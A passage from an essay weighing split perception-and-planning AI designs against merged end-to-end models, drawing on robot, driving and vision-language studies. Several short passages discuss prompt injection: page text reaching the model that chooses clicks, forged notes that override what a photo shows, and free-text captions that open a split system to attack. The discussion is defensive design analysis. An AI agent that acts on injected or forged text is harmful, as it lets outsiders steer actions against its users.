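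Choosing models from different companies may help, but the evidence conflicts. *Vision Verification Enhanced Fusion of VLMs for Efficient Visual Reasoning* (2026) found low error correlations between vision-language models with different architectures on college-level questions. But *Shared Item-Level Error Limits the Aggregation of Small Language Models* (2026) found error correlations of roughly 0.65 among 15 small language models estimating unknown quantities, and errors were not clearly more similar within a model family than across families. *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (2025) found that more accurate models tend to share more of their errors, so the problem may persist as models improve.

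A majority vote can be less accurate than the best single model. *Do Large Language Models Know Colombian Law?* (2026) reports that 15 models voting together answered 84.3% of questions about Colombian law correctly, compared with 90.5% for the best model alone. At least one model was right on 98.4% of the questions, but voting did not always select the right answer.

Asking the same model twice has the same weakness. Azran and colleagues' rule combines two readings of 80% into 94%, but if the second reading merely repeats the first, the right figure is still 80%. Getting different evidence usually helps more than asking a different model. Two models given the same photo of a clear liquid can't tell whether it is water or cleaning fluid, but a photo of the bottle's label might show which it is.

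## Would one model that both sees and plans avoid the problem?

A planner that asks for a photo of the bottle's label still receives only a description of that photo. Engineers could instead give the photo to a single model that chooses the action, so that *a* = *P*(*g*, *o*), without the intermediate description *d*. An early example is ALVINN, a small neural network from 1989 that turned camera and laser readings directly into steering commands, according to *End-to-End Learning vs. Modular Architectures*, a review of driving systems (Kapse, 2026). ALVINN's successors include end-to-end driving models and, in robotics, vision-language-action models, which take images and an instruction and output movements.

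A merged model has no fixed format that limits the information it can use to make a decision. Kapse notes that object detectors typically pass on a box and a label for each object and drop the rest of the scene. If a user wants a shirt without stains, a merged model can use the stained part of the photo even though nobody listed stains as something to report.

Training differs too. Engineers usually train a describing model to match human labels, whether or not a mistake would affect any action. In a merged model, the penalty for a bad action can correct the parts that process the image:

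∂*J*/∂*θ* = ∂*J*/∂*a* × ∂*a*/∂*h* × ∂*h*/∂*θ*

Here *J* is the penalty, *h* is the network's internal representation of the image, and *θ* stands for the settings that produce it. The model learns to tell navy from black if the difference changes which orders are correct. This chain breaks if *h* is a sentence, because words cannot change by small amounts. (Reinforcement learning can train a model through words, but it has to do so by trial and error.)

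### Robots

*TiPToP* compares its modular robot, which plans once from a three-dimensional record of the scene, with π0.5-DROID, a vision-language-action model. Engineers had fine-tuned π0.5-DROID on 350 hours of demonstrations, and it takes new images as it moves. Both systems received the same instructions and starting positions:

| Type of task | Modular robot | Vision-language-action model |
|---|---|---|
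| Simple | 22 of 40 | 27 of 40 |
| With distracting objects | 27 of 45 | 12 of 45 |
| Instruction needs interpretation | 26 of 40 | 10 of 40 |
| Several steps | 23 of 40 | 6 of 40 |
| All | 98 of 165 | 55 of 165 |

The modular system's lead depended partly on who ran the trials. It won 28 to 9 out of 40 on its developers' own robot, and 42 to 27 in 75 trials that an outside team ran on a real robot.

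The modular robot's worst result was in simulation, where it failed all ten attempts to put a banana in a bin, while the merged model succeeded in nine. Its record replaced each object with its convex hull, roughly the shape of a sheet stretched tightly around it, so the banana's inner curve disappeared. The merged model could also retry after a slipped grasp because it took new images, which a modular robot could do as well.

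More training data can reverse the result. On MolmoSpaces, a simulated benchmark, the modular robot succeeded 46% of the time, ahead of every merged model not trained on data from the same simulators. A merged model trained on such data reached about 60%.

Albinhassan, Russo and colleagues (2026), in *Neurosymbolic Embodied Agents*, separated the effect of the description from the effect of the planner. In two simulated households, a vision-language model either chose each action directly from the images or explored first and wrote a record of the relevant objects. The planner could then work from the record in several ways. These are success rates for the largest model they tested, Qwen3.5-27B:

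| What chose the actions | VirtualHome | ALFWorld |
|---|---|---|
| The model, from images | 62.5% | 26.9% |
| The model, reasoning from the record | 59.0% | 16.9% |
| The same, limited to actions the rules allow | 98.5% | 32.3% |
| A search over plans, without that limit | 99.0% | 29.2% |
| A search over allowed actions | 99.0% | 95.5% |

The record helped this model only when a program used it to check each action and search ahead, which would be hard to do with raw images. Smaller models benefited from the record alone, and the 4-billion-parameter version's score rose from 5.5% to 47.0% in VirtualHome.

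The comparison favours the split design in some ways, because the researchers gave it rules for what each action requires and changes, and a program to guide exploration, which the direct models did not have. A stronger merged model, Gemini 3 Flash, reached 91.0% in VirtualHome and 50.8% in ALFWorld without this help. Most of the split system's few remaining failures were perception errors, such as when a fork blended into a tabletop and was never added to the record.

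Even a correct record can be a worse input than an image. In *Vision-TL-Action* (2026), planning from images beat planning from the exact state of the objects by 8.3 percentage points on a robot arm, with a 95% interval of 1.6 to 15.4. In a maze, the two were about equal. Planning from the exact state did better in both settings when a task had to be done in a set order.

### Cars

UniAD is an end-to-end driving model whose parts for detecting objects, mapping the road and forecasting movement feed a learned planner. In *Old-School Planners Drive (Sometimes) Better Than Learned Ones*, Look (2026) kept UniAD's perception unchanged and replaced its planner with each of 16 textbook methods. These read UniAD's explicit outputs, such as its list of objects and their forecast paths, whereas UniAD's own planner uses the model's richer internal features.

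Across 436 simulated scenarios, nine of the 16 textbook planners scored higher than UniAD's learned planner, and the best scored 41.8 against UniAD's 32.0. UniAD hit a stationary car in 31 of 80 scenarios, while the best textbook planner did so in 13. So a good planner with a plain list of objects beat a weaker planner with more information. But UniAD is an older model, and WA-JEPA, a learned model from 2026, scored 44.9 on the same scenarios.

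The list also had gaps that hurt the textbook planner. UniAD's road masks often missed the branch the route took, so the car left the route more often in turns. UniAD's forecasts also did not include other cars steering at the car, and the textbook planner gained nothing against them.

In *Benchmarking Autonomous Driving Planners Across Leaderboards* (2025), planners that received the simulator's true state scored 72.0 to 75.1, while the best system that used sensors scored 53.6. The gap suggests how much a perfect description would help, but no real car receives one, so this doesn't show that a split design is better.

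A bottleneck can even help inside a merged model. *What Matters for Scalable and Robust Learning in End-to-End Driving Planners?* (2026) found that compressing the internal representation before it reached the planner made driving substantially more robust. This is consistent with the data processing inequality, which rules out a benefit from compression only for an ideal planner, and a trained planner is not ideal.

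### Why some developers keep an explicit layer

Tesla replaced its hand-written driving code with an end-to-end system because "codifying human values was really difficult", according to Understanding AI's *Waymo and Tesla’s self-driving systems are more similar than people think*. Waymo, which runs driverless taxis, has also moved towards merging models. Its *10 AI Lessons from Driving 200+ Million Fully Autonomous Miles* (2026) recommends a few large models over many small ones, which it calls "modular spaghetti".

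But the system Waymo describes in *Demonstrably Safe AI For Autonomous Driving* (2025) is not a single opaque model. Its parts exchange learned embeddings, which are lists of numbers that people can't read, and are trained together end to end. The system also produces explicit objects, their attributes and a map of the road. Waymo says it uses these outputs to check plans while the car is driving, run realistic simulations efficiently, and score the car's behaviour for evaluation and training. A separate safety system checks every proposed path against physical limits and traffic laws.

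A Waymo vice president told Axios that "pure end-to-end systems are not able to meet our safety bar". Waymo has not published a comparison that would let others test this claim. Axios' *Waymo says there's no AI shortcut to self-driving* (2026) points out that strict safety standards would favour Waymo over newer rivals such as Tesla, Wayve and Waabi.

### What merging gives up

In a split system, a log of the descriptions contains everything the planner received about the world. A merged model can also print a list of objects, but its action may not have depended on that list. Engineers also can no longer test each half separately. Look could attribute 31 of UniAD's 182 collisions to its planner because another planner finished the route with the same perception. *TiPToP* traces all 55 failures in 173 trials to particular modules, 31 of them to grasping and only 6 to the vision-language model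 that identified the objects.

Replaceable parts also save work. *TiPToP* reports moving its system to a different robot arm within a few hours and adding a whiteboard-wiping skill in under a day, both without retraining. A vision-language-action model would usually need new demonstrations for either change.

Merging the two models also makes it impossible to isolate the planner, because any instruction on a page reaches the model that chooses the next click. Engineers can still limit the model's tools or require approval for some actions, but they can't settle the plan before the model reads anything.

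### The same failures inside one model

A merged model can still misread the image. *Humanity's First Exam* (Kelly, Kementsietsidis et al., 2026) tested 18 recent models on 544 questions that are easy for people. Errors in visual perception accounted for 73% of wrong answers. The most common were misjudging a position, direction or path in an image (31%) and miscounting objects (23%).

More reasoning did little to fix these errors. Kelly and colleagues grouped the questions into sets of four similar ones, and a model passed a set only if it answered every question correctly on all four tries. When they reduced Gemini 4 Carbon's reasoning effort from high to low, its pass rate fell from 97.5% to 55.1% on mathematical and rule-following tasks, but only from 69.9% to 66.8% on vision tasks. A merged model that misreads an image is thus much like a planner given a false caption, because any further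 reasoning starts from the same mistake.

The models also gave little warning. They expressed doubt or offered an alternative in about 19% of their failures, ranging from 7% for OpenAI's models to 39% for Anthropic's.

The 73% partly reflects the choice of questions. More than half included an image, and the researchers kept only questions that some model had failed. The figure also depends on how a language model classified the causes, although a second model's classifications gave 72%. *HumanSightBench* (2026), which has 2,876 visual questions that people find easy, also reports consistent weaknesses across models.

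A model can also answer from what it expects instead of what the image shows. Vankadaru and DuTell (2026), in *Believing Is Seeing*, found that in eleven open models the outcome depends on how clear the image is and how strong the expectation is. Blurring the object that contradicted the expectation could change the answer, while degrading an equal area elsewhere did not. Strengthening the parts of the network that carry the image's influence corrected only 12% to 33% of the answers that had followed expectation.

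### When text and image disagree

Many merged agents receive text, such as captions, web pages or notes from memory, along with their images. If they follow the text when it conflicts with the images, the describing model's errors can again affect the plan. Deng and others called this tendency "blind faith in text" in a 2025 paper, according to *V-FAT* (2026).

Only some models show this tendency. *The Illusion of Grounding* (2026) tested models with a retrieved document that contradicted the image. Two LLaVA models favoured the document, while InternVL3 and Qwen2-VL favoured the image. Some of the apparent reliance on text was a preference for one of the two answers, whichever source supported it. For LLaVA-1.6, such preferences accounted for 40.6% of the paired tests and text-following accounted for 40.9%.

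Barua, Mahowald and Rudman (2026), in *Vision-Language Models Integrate Conflicting Evidence Like Biased Bayesian Observers*, explain the mixed results by separating the strength of the evidence from the weight a model gives it. A simple version of the idea is

score = *w*(image) × image evidence + *w*(text) × text evidence + prior

where evidence is the logarithm of the odds, and an ideal observer would give both sources a weight of 1. Suppose a photo favours water over cleaning fluid by 2 to 1, and a note favours cleaning fluid by 20 to 1. A model with weights of 0.9 for the image and 0.6 for the text gets 0.9 × ln 2 = 0.62 in favour of water and 0.6 × ln 20 = 1.80 in favour of cleaning fluid. It follows the note despite giving the photo more weight, and so would an ideal observer.

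Relying on text over a photo is a mistake only when the model gives the text more weight than it deserves. A forged note can look like strong evidence, so a model that can see the photo may still act on the note, as the shopping attacks showed. Most studies of text bias used small open models, and stronger models may weigh text and images better.

### Long tasks bring descriptions back

Vision-language-action models can carry out short movements but are unreliable in long procedures, according to *Towards Neuro-Symbolic Procedural Reasoning for Long-Horizon Vision-Language-Action Manipulation* (2026). The paper proposes adding a graph of the task's steps and a memory of what the robot has done. In *NS-VLA*, Zhu, Wu and colleagues (2026) gave such a model an explicit plan and a pointer to the current step, and success on a real robot rose from 40% to 60%. Both systems reintroduce a written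 record that can be wrong. If the pointer moves on too early, the robot may skip a step.

A merged model does not need another model to describe the current scene, but it still relies on descriptions of the past and of delegated work. If it works for hours, it runs out of context and its history is compacted like any other agent's. It also still has to hand large collections of files to subagents.

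### Choosing a design

Kapse proposes twelve yes-or-no questions for choosing a driving system's design, covering safety rules, surroundings, data and deployment. For seven of ten published systems, the design chosen this way at least partly matched the actual one. Ten systems is a small sample, and a match means the engineers made the same choice, which may not have been the best one.

How easily the planner can get the raw evidence may be the easiest condition to judge. A single photo is easy to pass on, so a planner that reads images well should normally receive it, with at most a caption added. A history of several million tokens doesn't fit in the planner's context window, so some description is unavoidable. Engineers can then gain more from pinned rules and links back to the source than from trying to merge the models.

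When the stakes are high, it is better to keep an explicit record alongside the raw evidence. Ordinary code can enforce a probability threshold for serving the glass of water only if some part of the system reports the probability as a separate value. The planner should also use the raw evidence, because the record may omit a danger nobody thought to list, such as a crack in the glass.

If outsiders can add text to what the agent reads, a split design protects the plan only when the planner can state its questions in advance and receives restricted answers. A split system that passes free-text captions to the planner can be easier to attack than a merged model, as seems to have happened in the shopping tests. When the task depends on what the agent reads, a merged model that has few tools and needs approval for risky actions may be better.

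The need for audits is the clearest reason to keep an explicit layer between perception and planning. The NTSB could reconstruct the Tempe crash from the software's labels and predicted paths. With a fully merged model, investigators would have had to infer what the software had taken the woman to be from the camera footage and steering commands.
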